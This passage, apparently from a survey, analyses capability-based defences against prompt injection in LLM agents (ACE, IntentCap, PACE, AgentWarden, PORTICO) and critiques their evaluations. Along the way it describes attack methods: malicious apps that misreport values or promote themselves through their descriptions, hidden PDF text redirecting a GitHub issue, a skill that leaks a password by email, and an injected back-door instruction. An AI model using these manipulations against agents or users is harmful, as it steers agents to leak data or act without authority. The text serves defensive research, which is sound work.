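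Plans are written in a subset of Python. They can contain conditions and loops, but every variable needs a declared type, and a plan can't open files, define functions, or import anything except the maths library. These limits make a plan easier to analyse before it runs. Li and colleagues chose Python because models write it well, but they concede that its behaviour is too complex for them to formally guarantee that their privacy checks are sound.

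### Matching the plan to installed apps

ACE next looks for an installed app to match each abstract one. It compares their descriptions numerically and discards installed apps that are too dissimilar. A second model then checks the remaining pairs one at a time to see whether the installed app could do the abstract app's job. It also writes an adapter if, for example, the two apps take their arguments in a different order.

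Judging each pair separately stops QuickRide from excluding MetroHail, because QuickRide's description isn't in the prompt when the model checks MetroHail against the first step. In the published trace, ACE matched both apps correctly and showed both fares.

QuickRide can still promote itself through its description, which the matching model has to read. If the description led the model to classify QuickRide as able to do MetroHail's job too, QuickRide would be a candidate for both steps. The user in the trace also made matching easier by naming both apps. A user who asked only for the fare might get a plan with a single fare calculator. ACE assigns exactly one installed app to each abstract app, so it might choose QuickRide and never run MetroHail.

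### Checking where private data can go

Before execution, ACE checks whether the plan would send private data to an app that isn't cleared for it. Each app has a clearance, and the user labels the request according to its sensitivity. In the simplest version, a label is a set of categories such as medical, financial and personal. If an app has clearance *C* and its inputs have labels *L₁* to *Lₙ*, ACE permits the call only when

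*L₁ ∪ … ∪ Lₙ ⊆ C*.

The output then gets the label *C*, because it may contain anything the app was cleared to see. In one example, a plan loads bank details through an app with financial clearance and passes them to an email app with only personal clearance. ACE rejects the plan because {financial} isn't a subset of {personal}. If no combination of installed apps satisfies the rule, the request ends with an error.

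The analysis also covers leaks through branches, as when a program writes 0 or 1 depending on a secret's first character. ACE adds the condition's label to everything computed inside its branches. In another example, a loop sends the contents of a variable over the network and then loads bank details into the same variable, so the first pass sends an empty string but the second would send the bank details. ACE repeats its analysis until the labels stop changing, so it finds this leak without running the loop.

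If the user labels the fare request as personal, QuickRide needs personal clearance to receive the two addresses. The label doesn't constrain what a cleared app does with the addresses once it has them, so an app whose container has network access could send them anywhere. The user also has to label every source of private data, and Li, Mallick and colleagues (2025) warn in an earlier version of the paper that the analysis won't detect leaks from unlabeled sources.

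### Running the two apps

A trusted program called the orchestrator starts one container for the plan and others for the apps. The plan's container has no access to the user's files and communicates only with the orchestrator. When the plan reaches the QuickRide step, the orchestrator starts QuickRide's container with the privileges assigned to that app, passes it the two addresses, and checks the type of the data it returns.

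QuickRide can't send a message to MetroHail or read its result, because all communication goes through the orchestrator. QuickRide also can't read the user's documents unless it has the privilege to use the file system, and the orchestrator stops it if it runs for too long. Li and colleagues exclude attacks in which an app breaks out of its container or infers secrets from side channels such as timing.

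QuickRide's instruction to misreport the fares now fails because the plan requires a fare. In the trace, the user sees MetroHail's fare of 51.4 and a type error in place of QuickRide's. The drug warning fails in the same way, and MetroHail still runs after it.

A false number would pass the type check. If the user had asked the assistant to book the cheaper ride, and the plan compared the two fares and booked the lower one, QuickRide could get the booking by returning a fare of $1. The attacker would have chosen between two branches of a plan produced from the user's request, without adding a step. Rajani and colleagues count this kind of influence as a value attack. ACE's secrecy labels don't prevent it, but AgentCap's policy could require a sensitive argument to come from a trusted source.

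A malicious app can do more harm when its output is text. If the planner had declared the fare as text, QuickRide's false comparison would have appeared on the user's screen. A text output can also go to another app that contains a language model, such as a summariser, and change what that app returns. The earlier version of the paper claims that app outputs never enter a language model's prompt. The design better supports the conference version's narrower claim that no model uses those outputs for control flow.

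### Privileges in place of references

Li and colleagues describe ACE as enforcing "data and capability barriers between apps". They use "capability" to mean a privilege of a container, such as access to the file system or the network. ACE confines each app with a sandbox policy rather than giving it unforgeable references to resources.

One of the paper's example plans passes the string `"file.txt"` to an app that loads documents. The app opens that file with its container's file-system access, and a different string would open a different file. If the file name came from another app's output, the loader could become a confused deputy, as Hardy's compiler did. In an object-capability version, the orchestrator would open the file the user had named and give the loader only a descriptor for it.

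As in object-capability systems, apps in ACE begin with no connection to each other, so a user can install a malicious app without connecting it to the honest ones. But ACE creates this separation through the container's settings, and within those settings an app has ambient authority over whatever its privileges cover.

According to the earlier version of the paper, each app's developer assigns its privileges. If two combinations of apps could carry out the plan and one's privileges are a strict subset of the other's, ACE chooses the one with fewer privileges. For example, it would choose a combination that needs files and the network over one that also needs control of the system. This rule reduces the damage an app can do, but an attacker can exploit it by requesting fewer privileges. A malicious fare calculator that requests none would be chosen over a legitimate one that needs the network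 to look up prices. The malicious app couldn't read files or send data out, but it could still return a false fare.

### The security tests

Li and colleagues ran their three attacks against ACE and report that all failed, whichever models did the planning. They support this with individual traces and don't say how many times they ran each attack.

Li and colleagues also adapted InjecAgent, which normally starts each test after the agent has fetched the hostile text. In their version, ACE first had to plan the request and find the right app. They counted an attack as successful if an attacker's app ran, and a task as successful if the expected app ran without an error.

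| Planning and matching models | Attacker's app ran (1,054 cases) | Expected app ran |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o and o3-mini | 0 | 85.3% |
| GPT-4o | 0 | 83.6% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 0 | 60.7% |
| Qwen-2.5-72B | 0 | 60.2% |

The zeros follow almost directly from the design, because InjecAgent's attacks all need an extra call and ACE can't add a call once it has read an app's output. The zeros are good evidence that the software enforces the plan, but they give no information about attacks that use the plan's own steps. Some cases also didn't test the attack. With Claude, the expected app didn't run successfully in about 410 cases, and in many of these the hostile text never arrived because ACE had found no suitable app.

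For comparison, Li and colleagues tested a version of Mistral-7B trained with StruQ, which teaches a model to distinguish instructions from data. Attacks on it succeeded 7% of the time. Mistral-7B is much smaller than the model used with ACE, so the result is weak evidence of how ACE compares with training a stronger model to resist attacks.

*Agent Security Bench (ASB)* (2024) covers several kinds of attack on agents and defences against them. Li and colleagues tested ACE on its indirect injections, which involve 10 agents in different settings and 50 user requests. An attacker's app ran in three of 2,000 trials (0.15%). The expected app ran in at least 86% of cases with both GPT-4o and GPT-4.1.

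Li and colleagues don't count the three calls as security violations, because the injected text didn't cause them. In one, a user asked about the risks and returns of investing in a new sector. The planner invented an app called `MarketDataAnalysis`, and ACE matched it to the attacker's `MarketAnalysisTool`, whose description fitted the task. Excluding these cases is reasonable in a test of prompt injection. But ACE is also supposed to withstand attackers who write their own apps' descriptions, and a description that fits a common task is the obvious way to get a malicious app selected. The app would then receive the user's data and could return whatever investment advice its developer wanted. None of the published tests measures how often attackers would succeed by writing descriptions for this purpose.

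### Utility and cost

InjecAgent and ASB simulate their apps crudely, and neither checks whether the user got a correct answer. Li and colleagues therefore also used LangChain's Tool Usage benchmark, which contains no attacks. In its first suite, the agent types a word by calling one tool once per letter. In the second, it does the same with 26 tools, one for each letter. In the third, it answers questions about a small database, which it queries with 17 tools. The table gives the share of tasks in which the final answer and the state of the simulated environment were both correct.

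| Suite | GPT-4o | GPT-4.1 | GPT-4o and o3-mini |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single tool | 100% | 95.0% | 100% |
| Multiple tools | 80.0% | 80.0% | 80.0% |
| Relational data | 81.0% | 85.7% | 66.7% |

On the database questions, ACE made exactly the expected sequence of calls in 47.6% to 76.2% of tasks, less often than it answered correctly, so it sometimes reached the right answer with a different sequence. The percentages are consistent with suites of 20 or 21 tasks, where each task counts for about five percentage points. Li and colleagues don't report how an ordinary agent performed on the same tasks with the same models, so the results don't show how much ACE reduces accuracy.

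Average cost per request ranged from $0.01 to $0.55, and average time from 11 to 48 seconds. The suite with 26 tools was the most expensive, because ACE may have to query a model about every pairing of an abstract app with an installed one. With GPT-4.1, the single-tool suite took 11.73 seconds per request, compared with 39.21 seconds in IsolateGPT's published results. The comparison is rough because the figures come from separate experiments.

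### Independent tests of similar designs

No independent evaluation of ACE appears to have been published. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026), a preliminary report that has not been peer-reviewed, describes a general shortage of independent tests that use adapted attacks against defences outside the model.

Like ACE, CaMeL turns the user's request into a program before the agent reads any outside data, according to *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026). *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) tested CaMeL against injections that tamper with the user's task instead of replacing it. Attack success was between 1.0% and 1.7%, but the agents appear to have completed only about 13% of tasks without an attack and 14% with one. An agent that finishes so few tasks also gives an attacker few opportunities. The researchers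 wrote CaMeL's policies for their own benchmark, so those policies may partly explain the low completion rates.

*INFUSE* (2026) found the opposite on security. Across five models, with 200 combinations of attack and task in each condition, a "CaMeL-style" control did not reduce attack success by an amount distinguishable from chance. The researchers had adapted CaMeL's design to agents that work through a command shell, and they limit their conclusion to that adaptation. A shell is a hard case for any system that controls which tools run, because one tool can execute almost any command. Neither test transfers directly to ACE, which adds isolated apps and lacks CaMeL's checks on where sensitive arguments came from.

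### Requests that nobody can plan in advance

A fixed plan can handle variation that the planner foresees. For example, one database question is whether Bob and Alice live in the same city. Before seeing any data, ACE writes a program that looks up both users, finds their locations, compares the cities and chooses one of two answers. The program also includes a message in case there is no Bob. But if there are several Bobs, it continues with the first one. An ordinary agent would see the list and could ask the user which Bob they meant.

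For other requests, the steps are in the data. The user in Progent's example wanted an agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice had emailed, and no planner could write a program for this without reading her email. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) includes a similar task, in which the user asks an agent to install a Python package by following the steps in a Reddit post. A fixed plan could retrieve the post, but it couldn't contain commands that only the post specifies.

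Planning in advance is even harder on the web, because a browser agent may not know what a button does, or that it exists, until it loads the page. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* points out that researchers have applied this approach only in simple settings, where the agent has a few tools and knows their effects beforehand. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (2026) nevertheless argues that web agents should fix their programs in advance by default and use trusted website APIs instead of clicking. Web content could then change the data a program processes, but not add actions.

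Li and colleagues don't discuss requests whose steps are in untrusted data. They limit ACE to single requests and standalone apps, and leave conversations and suites of related apps to future work. Their planner is also limited because it must guess which apps are likely to exist. They argue that most apps fall into familiar groups, such as loading files or processing text, and the optional description of the setting helps. On InjecAgent, ACE still failed to match the expected app in 12% to 33% of cases, depending on the models and excluding requests that failed earlier.

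Several newer designs let planning continue but restrict what information reaches the planner. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026), the planner chooses its steps as it goes, but variable names stand in for untrusted data. It can query a second, isolated model about the data, but the answers are hidden too. The agent in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* works with similar placeholders and must get each value approved before using it. In the installation task, its first attempt to approve the command from the post failed because the command requested a permission the planner hadn't declared. The second attempt succeeded because the command was a standard operation.

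In another of its tasks, the user asked the agent to copy a plugin's address from a forum thread and download the plugin. The thread contained an address with one letter of the owner's name changed. A program fixed in advance would have passed the false address to the download step. The agent compared the address with the model's existing information about the plugin and found a mismatch.

*Kaer* (2026) argues that a fixed plan has to account for every course that execution could take, so it starts with a minimal plan and permits changes only after a step has failed. An agent that can't complete its step may report only one of a fixed list of failure conditions, since a malicious agent could hide instructions in a free-text explanation. Fixed rules then modify the unfinished part of the plan. A malicious agent can still lie about why it failed and so influence which repair the system makes,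 but it can't write a new step.

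## Granting capabilities by task and by source of content

ACE fixes an agent's steps before the agent reads any outside data. IntentCap and PACE, two systems from autumn 2026, let the agent choose its steps as it goes. Both systems derive a grant of capabilities from the user's request and check each proposed tool call against it, so their protection depends on how accurately software can determine what a request permits.

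### IntentCap: one source for each field

*LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (Zheng, Zhang and Mao, 2026) describes a user who selects two PDFs and asks an agent to extract their tables, save them as spreadsheets and open one GitHub issue in the repository `org/proj`. Hidden text in one PDF tells the agent to create the issue in `attacker/repo`. A list of permitted websites wouldn't stop this, because both repositories are on GitHub. The same error can happen without an attacker if the agent mistakes a table heading for the repository's name.

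IntentCap sorts everything the agent reads into four sources. The user's request supplies the goal, the chosen files, the destinations and any approvals. Workflow instructions, such as a Skill (a package of instructions for one kind of task), supply the procedure. A tool's schema supplies the arguments the tool accepts and the scope of its credentials. The runtime environment, which includes tool results and file contents, supplies observed values. Each field of a capability accepts values only from its one assigned source.

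Trusted software first extracts the most that the user has authorized. A language model then proposes a lease, a short-lived capability for one operation. For the GitHub issue, it would look roughly like this:

```
operation:    create_issue
repository:   org/proj      (copied from the user's request)
issue body:   table values  (data from the PDFs)
budget:       1 issue
expires:      after first use
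```

The design allows for an attacker controlling the model that writes the lease, because that model only makes proposals. A deterministic checker accepts a lease only if it stays within what the user authorized. The repository field also needs a witness, a pointer to the words in the user's request that contain the name. If the hidden text misleads the agent, the model proposes a lease for `attacker/repo`. The user never wrote that name, so there is no witness, and the checker denies the lease before the tool runs.

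AgentCap's provenance check could also reject the attacker's repository, but only if the developer had listed that argument as sensitive. IntentCap gives every field an owner, so the developer has less to remember. Someone must still decide which fields hold only data and may therefore be influenced by the PDF. An attacker could use one of these fields, such as the issue's body, to publish a false figure or a malicious link.

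Paying an attached bill is as hard for IntentCap as for AgentCap, because an account number that appears only in the bill has no witness. Pasting the bill into the chat wouldn't help, because the prototype doesn't let pasted documents fill fields that carry authority. Zheng and colleagues allow an exception for "user-authorized selectors", which might let a user specify that the payee should come from a particular file, but they don't describe how a selector works. They also don't explain how the trusted software finds destinations and approvals in ordinary prose, rather than in a form where the user picks them.

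### IntentCap on replayed events

Zheng and colleagues tested IntentCap's checker on events replayed from AgentDojo, InjecAgent, τ²-bench and MCPTox, a benchmark of poisoned tool descriptions. IntentCap wrongly accepted none of 3,746 security-sensitive events. It covered all 3,813 legitimate actions in a test modelled on τ²-bench and passed 2,554 of 2,556 applicable ground-truth checks.

These figures come from a replay in which no live agent had to finish a task, so they don't measure attack success or utility. The replay doesn't capture how an agent might respond to a refusal, such as by retrying, giving up or finding another route. Zheng and colleagues leave to future work end-to-end attack success, the checker's speed, and adapted attacks on the labeling and the leases.

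An ablation of IntentCap merged all four sources into one trusted source. The checker then accepted 94% of the events it should have denied (3,593 of 3,823). Merging only two sources at a time caused errors in 43% to 50% of these events. The checker therefore relies almost entirely on the distinctions between sources to deny these events, and a wrong label on a piece of text could undo the protection. IntentCap labels most text by its position, so user messages count as the user's intent and tool responses count as the runtime environment. Position is hard for an attacker to forge, but labeling by position doesn't help if the software puts an attacker's text in the wrong position.

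Zheng and colleagues also labeled the right scope for 24 leases by hand. IntentCap matched every label, while each alternative they tried granted too much in at least some cases. With only 24 examples, all labeled by the system's designers, this is weak evidence that IntentCap would scope other requests correctly.

### PACE: a check immediately before the effect

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) considers a mail skill whose code always calls `send_email(body)` and whose written instructions tell the model how to compose the body. A safe version prescribes a fixed template, while a malicious one tells the model to copy in a password from its context. Both versions have the same code, so inspecting it can't distinguish them. The paper proves that if a review procedure gives the same result for a safe version and a leaking one, no sound gate that relies on that result can exempt either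 version from later checks. PACE therefore checks every call at the last boundary before the tool runs, when the actual arguments exist and software can still stop the call from taking effect.

The first of its two checks is path confinement. PACE keeps a graph of the values, resources and operations in a session and of the data flows between them. It marks secrets and anything from an untrusted origin. If a path leads from a marked value to an unsafe effect, such as an outgoing email, PACE has to cut the path. It can't change past calls, so it can only block the present call or sever every argument through which marked data enters. The cheapest cut therefore costs

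*min(cost of blocking the call, total cost of severing the affected arguments)*.

Severing an argument means replacing it with a value that doesn't depend on the original. PACE also requires a guarantee that the original didn't influence whether the call happened. Developers can rarely give that guarantee when a language model chose the call, so in practice PACE nearly always blocks the call instead of severing the argument.

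The second check, capability and effect verification, compares what the call would do with what the user authorized. Deterministic software compiles the user's request into a capability with limits on purpose, resource, arguments, number of uses, lifetime and delegation. Text written by a model can't create or widen this capability. The call must then meet nine obligations. For example, the capability must cover the operation, the arguments must match it, and the call must not disclose confidential data.

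Suppose a user has the malicious mail skill and asks the agent to send Ana a project summary. The model follows the skill's instructions and puts a password in the body. PACE recognises the registered password even if the model has encoded it in base64. A path leads from the password to the email, so path confinement blocks the call, and the obligation on confidentiality should fail too. If the skill had instead told the model to send the summary to a stranger, the capability wouldn't have covered the recipient. A paraphrased or fragmented secret could still get through, because PACE checks for only a fixed set of encodings.

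### The certified contract and the tested configuration

If the skill is benign but the summary draws on a web page, path confinement blocks an email that the user asked for, because the page is untrusted and a path leads from it to the email. PACE-C, the certified contract, never restores a blocked call, so the email stays blocked. PACE-C also checks the final form of any call it has changed.

All the experiments used a more permissive configuration, PACE-P. It restores a blocked call if effect verification approves the call, so Ana gets her summary. It can also repair a call in a way the developer declared in advance, without checking the repaired call again. It releases low-impact calls even if they exceed the user's authorization or budget. Low-impact calls are reversible, send nothing out, and leave nothing behind.

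The proof that no recorded path reaches the effect doesn't cover a restored call, because that path still exists. PACE-P keeps a weaker guarantee. If the labels and schemas are correct and no call avoids the check, an unauthorized outward or irreversible effect can happen only through one of the declared repairs. On the tasks recorded from AgentDyn, path confinement proposed a cut for 5,842 of 6,647 calls. No arguments were rewritten, and the agent could work only because effect verification overrode the blocks.

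IntentCap and PACE, like AgentCap, check whether a grant fits the model's plain-text call instead of giving the agent an object reference. But their grants are closer to capabilities than AgentCap's, because they come from one user's request rather than a standing policy.

### Seventy-nine columns

Li, Wang and colleagues ran eight benchmarks on gpt-5.6-luna, DeepSeek-V4-Flash and Qwen-3.8-27B. Each column in their results covers one group of attacks from one benchmark against one model, and compares PACE-P with the undefended agent and the other defences tested on that benchmark. AgentDojo has nine columns, for three styles of injection against each of the three models.

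There were 84 columns. The researchers dropped three that measure only the second half of a data theft and two in which the undefended agent resisted every attack. PACE-P had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of the remaining 79, tied for lowest in 14 and was higher in three. In those three, the defence with the lowest rate also did less useful work, and in one case it completed no user tasks at all. A count of columns gives more weight to benchmarks with many attack groups and ignores the size of the differences, so the rates themselves are more informative. These are the AgentDojo results, with the most successful style of injection for each defence:

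| Model | Attack success, undefended | CaMeL | Progent | PACE-P | Utility, undefended | Utility, PACE-P |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-3.8-27B | 48.00% | 0.32% | 3.02% | 0% | 62.59% | 59.67% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 99.84% | 28.14% | 61.53% | 5.09% | 75.68% | 75.25% |
| gpt-5.6-luna | 100% | 36.09% | 69.00% | 8.11% | 73.77% | 72.05% |

PACE-P made a large difference and reduced utility only slightly, by at most 2.92 points on any of the full benchmarks compared with no defence. However, the policies and schemas were specific to each benchmark, and the researchers developed them knowing its task formats. AgentCap's designers had the same advantage.

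The comparison with other defences is less convincing. Progent's developers reported a 1.0% attack success rate on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, and Odersky and colleagues cite one successful attack in 963 for CaMeL with o4-mini-high. Rates of 69% and 36% are so much higher that the local versions may not have run as their designers intended, though different models could explain part of the gap.

The published tables also contain errors. CaMeL's figures on PASB, a benchmark for personal agents, repeat five consecutive numbers from a different defence's results on ASB. One of PACE-P's three losing rates is printed as 0.06%, but a single success in that column would be 0.56%. Neither error changes the count of 62, 14 and three.

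### Which component did the work

To separate PACE's components, the researchers ran 1,167 cases on Qwen with every combination of path confinement, effect verification and a third component, boundary adaptation, which adjusts how the software handles calls at the moment of execution. Five of the eight combinations show the pattern:

| Components | AgentDojo attack success | AgentDojo utility | AgentDyn attack success | AgentDyn utility | MCPTox refusals |
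|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% | 42.2% |
| Path confinement | 0% | 13.6% | 0% | 0% | 78.4% |
| Effect verification | 0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% | 99.3% |
| Effect verification and adaptation | 0% | 66.2% | 0% | 31.7% | 1.6% |
| All three | 0% | 67.2% | 0% | 33.3% | 2.3% |

Path confinement has the most elaborate proof of PACE's three components but contributed least to its results. Used alone, it stopped these attacks by blocking most of the agent's work. Effect verification also stopped nearly all of them and left the agent much more useful. Adding path confinement to the other two components changed little, except on the web benchmark WASP, where it coincided with three fewer successful attacks out of 24. Boundary adaptation alone also stopped all 24, so even this benefit didn't require path confinement. Li, Wang and colleagues concede that they haven't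 demonstrated a security benefit specific to the full combination.

The ablation doesn't match the main results well. PACE-P completed 20 of 60 AgentDyn cases in the ablation but 339 of 560 on the full benchmark, which the researchers attribute to the mix of tasks. The undefended agent resisted all 280 ASB cases in the ablation, although 13% to 89% of ASB attacks succeeded against the same model in the main tests. The ablation is therefore more useful for comparing components than for predicting how much protection a user would get.

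### The adaptive search

Before the adaptive test, the researchers checked the attacker's intended call in all 629 AgentDojo pairs against the authority compiled from the user's request. In 375 pairs (59.6%), the call fell outside that authority. They drew ten of these pairs from each of the Slack, Travel and Workspace suites and none from Banking.

A program then tried to improve the injection for each pair, using the agent's calls and PACE's reasons for refusing them. It wrote four new versions per round and stopped at the first success or after 50 attempts. Without a defence, the attack succeeded in 21 of 30 pairs. Against PACE-P, it succeeded in none of the 30 pairs over 1,500 attempts, which is compatible with a true success rate of up to 11.4% of such pairs.

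The agent proposed the attacker's exact call 157 times, and PACE refused it every time. This is good evidence that rewording an injection doesn't widen the user's grant. But the agent never proposed the call in 16 of the 30 pairs, so those pairs didn't test the check. The same Qwen model was also both the target of the attacks and the program that rewrote them, and a stronger model might have rewritten them better.

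The choice of pairs matters more, because the test covered only goals that the authorization obligation was already known to refuse. In the other 254 pairs, the attacker's call passes that obligation, and only the remaining checks can stop it. An attacker who understood PACE would choose a goal of this second kind. Debenedetti and colleagues found that a task's own tools were enough for the attack in 17% of AgentDojo cases. PACE's authorization obligation let the attacker's call through in 40%, so the compiled grants were probably broader than many tasks needed.

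### AgentWarden: hiding tools by type of task

*Beyond Static Sandboxing* (Sidik and Rokach, 2026) presents AgentWarden, which applies capability gating to OpenClaw, an open-source personal agent that makes every tool visible in every session by default. A small model classifies the user's first message as one of six task types, such as email or web research, and AgentWarden shows the agent only the tools for that type. For a summary, it shows four tools instead of 15, and a configuration setting blocks any calls to the hidden ones. A separate component checks each call for dangerous commands.

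AgentWarden was supposed to learn the smallest useful set of tools from its log of past sessions. The training rewarded completed tasks and penalized unused tools and blocked calls. In production testing, both trained versions offered the agent only `memory_search`, whatever the task. Sidik and Rokach blame the simulated training sessions, in which agents always used a fixed fraction of the tools they saw. AgentWarden now detects this failure and falls back on hand-written rules.

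Sidik and Rokach tested AgentWarden on a batch of 500 tasks, 100 of which were adversarial, including prompts to ignore all restrictions and run shell commands. AgentWarden blocked 38 of the adversarial tasks, the model refused 54, and the other eight led to no dangerous call. The agent received these tasks directly, so the test provides little evidence about instructions hidden in a file.

AgentWarden barely helped against the hidden instructions in AgentDojo. Across 949 cases with the model deepseek-chat, attack success fell from 90.3% to 88.9%, and utility without an attack fell from 90.7% to 89.7%. Sidik and Rokach attribute this to the attacks arriving in tool outputs, while AgentWarden governs tool calls. But most of AgentDojo's attackers need a tool call to reach their goal. A likelier explanation is that AgentWarden's six broad task types, designed around OpenClaw's tools, left the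 tools the attackers needed available. AgentDojo's own tool filter, which chose tools for each request, reduced attack success to 7.5% with GPT-4o.

AgentWarden also withheld access that users needed. It couldn't classify about 12% of sessions and gave them only tools for reading and searching, which would stop any session that had to write a file. In the batch of 500 tasks, its call classifier blocked about 22 legitimate writes.

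### Grants that are too narrow and too broad

Better models may still fail to work out what access a task needs. The AuthBench benchmark asks coding agents to write file-access policies for a task. According to *DelegationBench* (2026), it scores whether a policy permits enough and whether it permits too much. *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (Tu and Tu, 2026) reports that frontier models both withhold access the task requires and grant access it doesn't. *Trust Is Not a Score* (2026) concludes that authority can't be adjusted along a single scale. Making such a model more cautious would remove some unnecessary permissions, but it would also remove more of the necessary ones.

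A model can drop a necessary condition when it translates a policy into access rules. *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026), which studied general access-control rules rather than agents' tools, gives the example of a model turning a rule for "the assigned nurse" into a rule for every nurse. When a model wrote the rules in one step, 60% of policies that depended on ownership lacked the necessary condition. For policies meant to deny an action, 62.5% of the generated rules were wrong, often because they contained no active prohibition. A reviewer could easily miss these errors because the faulty rules can still compile.

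Users often don't state what an agent is authorized to do. *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026) compared prompts that state the authorized scope with prompts that don't. Without the statement, the rate at which agents exceeded their scope rose by 11.9 to 17.2 percentage points, with no attacker involved. *DelegationBench* describes another benchmark, AuthorizationBench, in which between 10.5% and 26.6% of runs included an action the agent had no authority to take. Prompt injection led to such actions less often than ordinary pressure did.

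Agents in AuthorizationBench that asked the user first overstepped less often. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) presents PAUTH, which derives authorization from the text of the task and blocks calls that the text doesn't specify well enough. To avoid repeatedly asking the user, the agent can fill in missing details before it submits the task. For a bill, that would mean copying the payee's account number from the bill into the task. If an attacker had changed the number on the bill, PAUTH would authorize a payment to the attacker unless the user checked the number first.

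Users may approve permission prompts without checking them. Tu and Tu report Anthropic's finding that users of its coding agent accepted about 93% of prompts. Anthropic responded with a classifier that approves or blocks actions automatically. The classifier missed 17% of 52 overeager actions in Anthropic's own test, and its miss rate was as high as 81% in an outside test.

Tu and Tu instead trained a small model, Qwen3.5-4B, to use less authority. They defined how much authority each task needed and penalized the model for exceeding it. On 500 new tasks, the share of runs that finished safely rose from 64.36% to 98.48%, and the share with excess authority fell from 4.56% to 0.79%. Most of the improvement came from completing tasks correctly, since excess authority was already uncommon. The tasks were synthetic, and the researchers had to specify how much authority each one needed, information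 that real requests usually lack. They recommend using the training in addition to permission checks and sandboxes.

### When the model that decides has read the attack

An inference error is more dangerous if an attacker can cause it. *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) observes that a model which writes and enforces policy at run time is still exposed to the injection. The paper also tested models that select a policy, and adapted attacks breached them in around 10% of AgentDojo's Banking scenarios and in none from the other three suites.

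Shi and colleagues' adapted attacks on Progent's rule-writing model had little effect. One was an instruction to allow all tools if the model was updating the policy. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* reports that attack success stayed between roughly 0.5% and 4.2%. With automatic approval, though, only the model's output kept the rules from allowing more.

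A fixed upper limit reduces the damage from a bad judgment. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) describes a system in which a classifier predicts permissions from the task's description. If an attacker has tampered with the description, the classifier predicts too many permissions. The system therefore grants a predicted permission only if it falls within the limits for the user's department and doesn't form a forbidden combination with others. IntentCap's limit is tighter because it comes from the individual request. A hijacked model can propose a useless lease or choose the wrong one of two destinations the user named, but it can't add a third. PACE compiles the grant without using a model.

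Attackers can also exploit a system that becomes stricter. *Poisoning Self-Evolving Security Policies in LLM Agents* (2026) attacks a defense in which a model writes new rules after seeing harmful behavior. After the agent follows a single injected instruction, the model writes a rule so broad that the agent begins to refuse legitimate work. The attack worked with Nemotron and, less reliably, with gpt-oss-120b. It failed with agents that resisted the original injection. Later normal use could weaken the rule's effect but didn't remove the rule.

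## Granting and withdrawing capabilities during a run

A permission that fits the task when it is granted can become too broad later in the run. Suppose a user asks a coding agent to add a timeout setting to a program. Most of the work is in `src/api.py`, but the agent also has to change `src/serialization.py`, so it gets permission to write to that file. The tests pass, and the agent moves on. If it then reads a web page with an injected instruction to put a back door in that file, it still has permission to do so. In *Lingering Authority*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) uses the title phrase for a temporary permission that stays available after the subtask that justified it has ended.

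An expiry time, like the one on AgentCap's tokens, only approximates the end of a subtask, because nobody knows beforehand how long the work will take.

### PORTICO: handles that close with the subtask

Santos-Grueiro's system, PORTICO, sits between the model and its tools. It follows a contract for each task, which a developer writes in advance. In simplified form, the contract for the timeout task is:

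```
at the start:   read and write src/api.py and its test
on request:     read and write src/serialization.py
until:          the tests pass or the subtask ends
never:          read notes/packaging.md, use the network
```

When the agent asks for the serialization file, PORTICO checks the request against the contract and creates a handle, such as `g0001:r1`, without opening the file. From the next turn on, the model can use the handle in its tool calls, and PORTICO looks it up in a table outside the model. The handle works only for this task, file, kind of access and grant period. When the tests pass, PORTICO removes the handle from the options shown to the model and rejects any later call that uses it.

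PORTICO ignores the model's claims that a subtask is still going on or that a new one has begun, because an injection could have led the model to make them. It closes a grant only after a trusted event, such as a test run that PORTICO launched, a change of phase in the software that manages the task, or a decision by an authenticated person. Reopening the grant requires a new trusted event.

PORTICO's handles resemble Unix file descriptors. They are closer to object capabilities than AgentCap's tokens are, because the model has to select a handle instead of naming the file. Closing a handle revokes access, as turning off Redell's forwarder does, even if the model still has the handle's label in its context. But the agent requests its handles by file name, so the contract has to determine which names are acceptable.

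While a handle is open, an injection can still make the agent write something harmful to the file. Shell commands are also difficult because one command can touch many files. PORTICO tries to work out a command's effects before running it, and blocks any command it can't classify unless someone approves it.

### Tests with and without revocation

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same grants at the same moments but never withdrew them. In each test, the agent used a grant legitimately and then tried to use it again after the subtask had closed.

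| Attempted late use | What chose the calls | Allowed by PORTICO | Allowed without revocation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading a file again | Qwen3-Coder 30B | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Writing to a file | Fixed script | 0 of 6 | 6 of 6 |
| File, Git and network actions | Fixed script | 0 of 6 | 6 of 6 |
| The same kinds of action, after an injected instruction | Qwen3-Coder 30B | 0 of 6 | 6 of 6 |

The scripted tests confirm that the enforcement code follows its rule. The last row is better evidence of a real danger, because a live model followed the injected instruction in all six cases when the grant was still open. But the cases were constructed, and Santos-Grueiro doesn't present them as an estimate of how often such attacks succeed.

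A broader test placed tempting but forbidden resources within the agent's reach in 17 scenarios. The agent broke the contract in every run with unrestricted access, in 86% of runs with a sandbox, in 82% with a fixed list of permissions, and in none with PORTICO. As in ScopeGate's tests, a violation meant breaking the system's own rules, so the test couldn't detect mistakes in the contract.

PORTICO also removes closed handles from the model's options, which is meant to reduce forbidden attempts. The evidence that it does is mixed. Compared with a version that enforced the same rules but showed the model more options, PORTICO blocked fewer attempts in one group of tasks (67 against 84) and more in another (48 against 39). Both versions blocked every forbidden attempt, so the protection came from the check at the moment of use.

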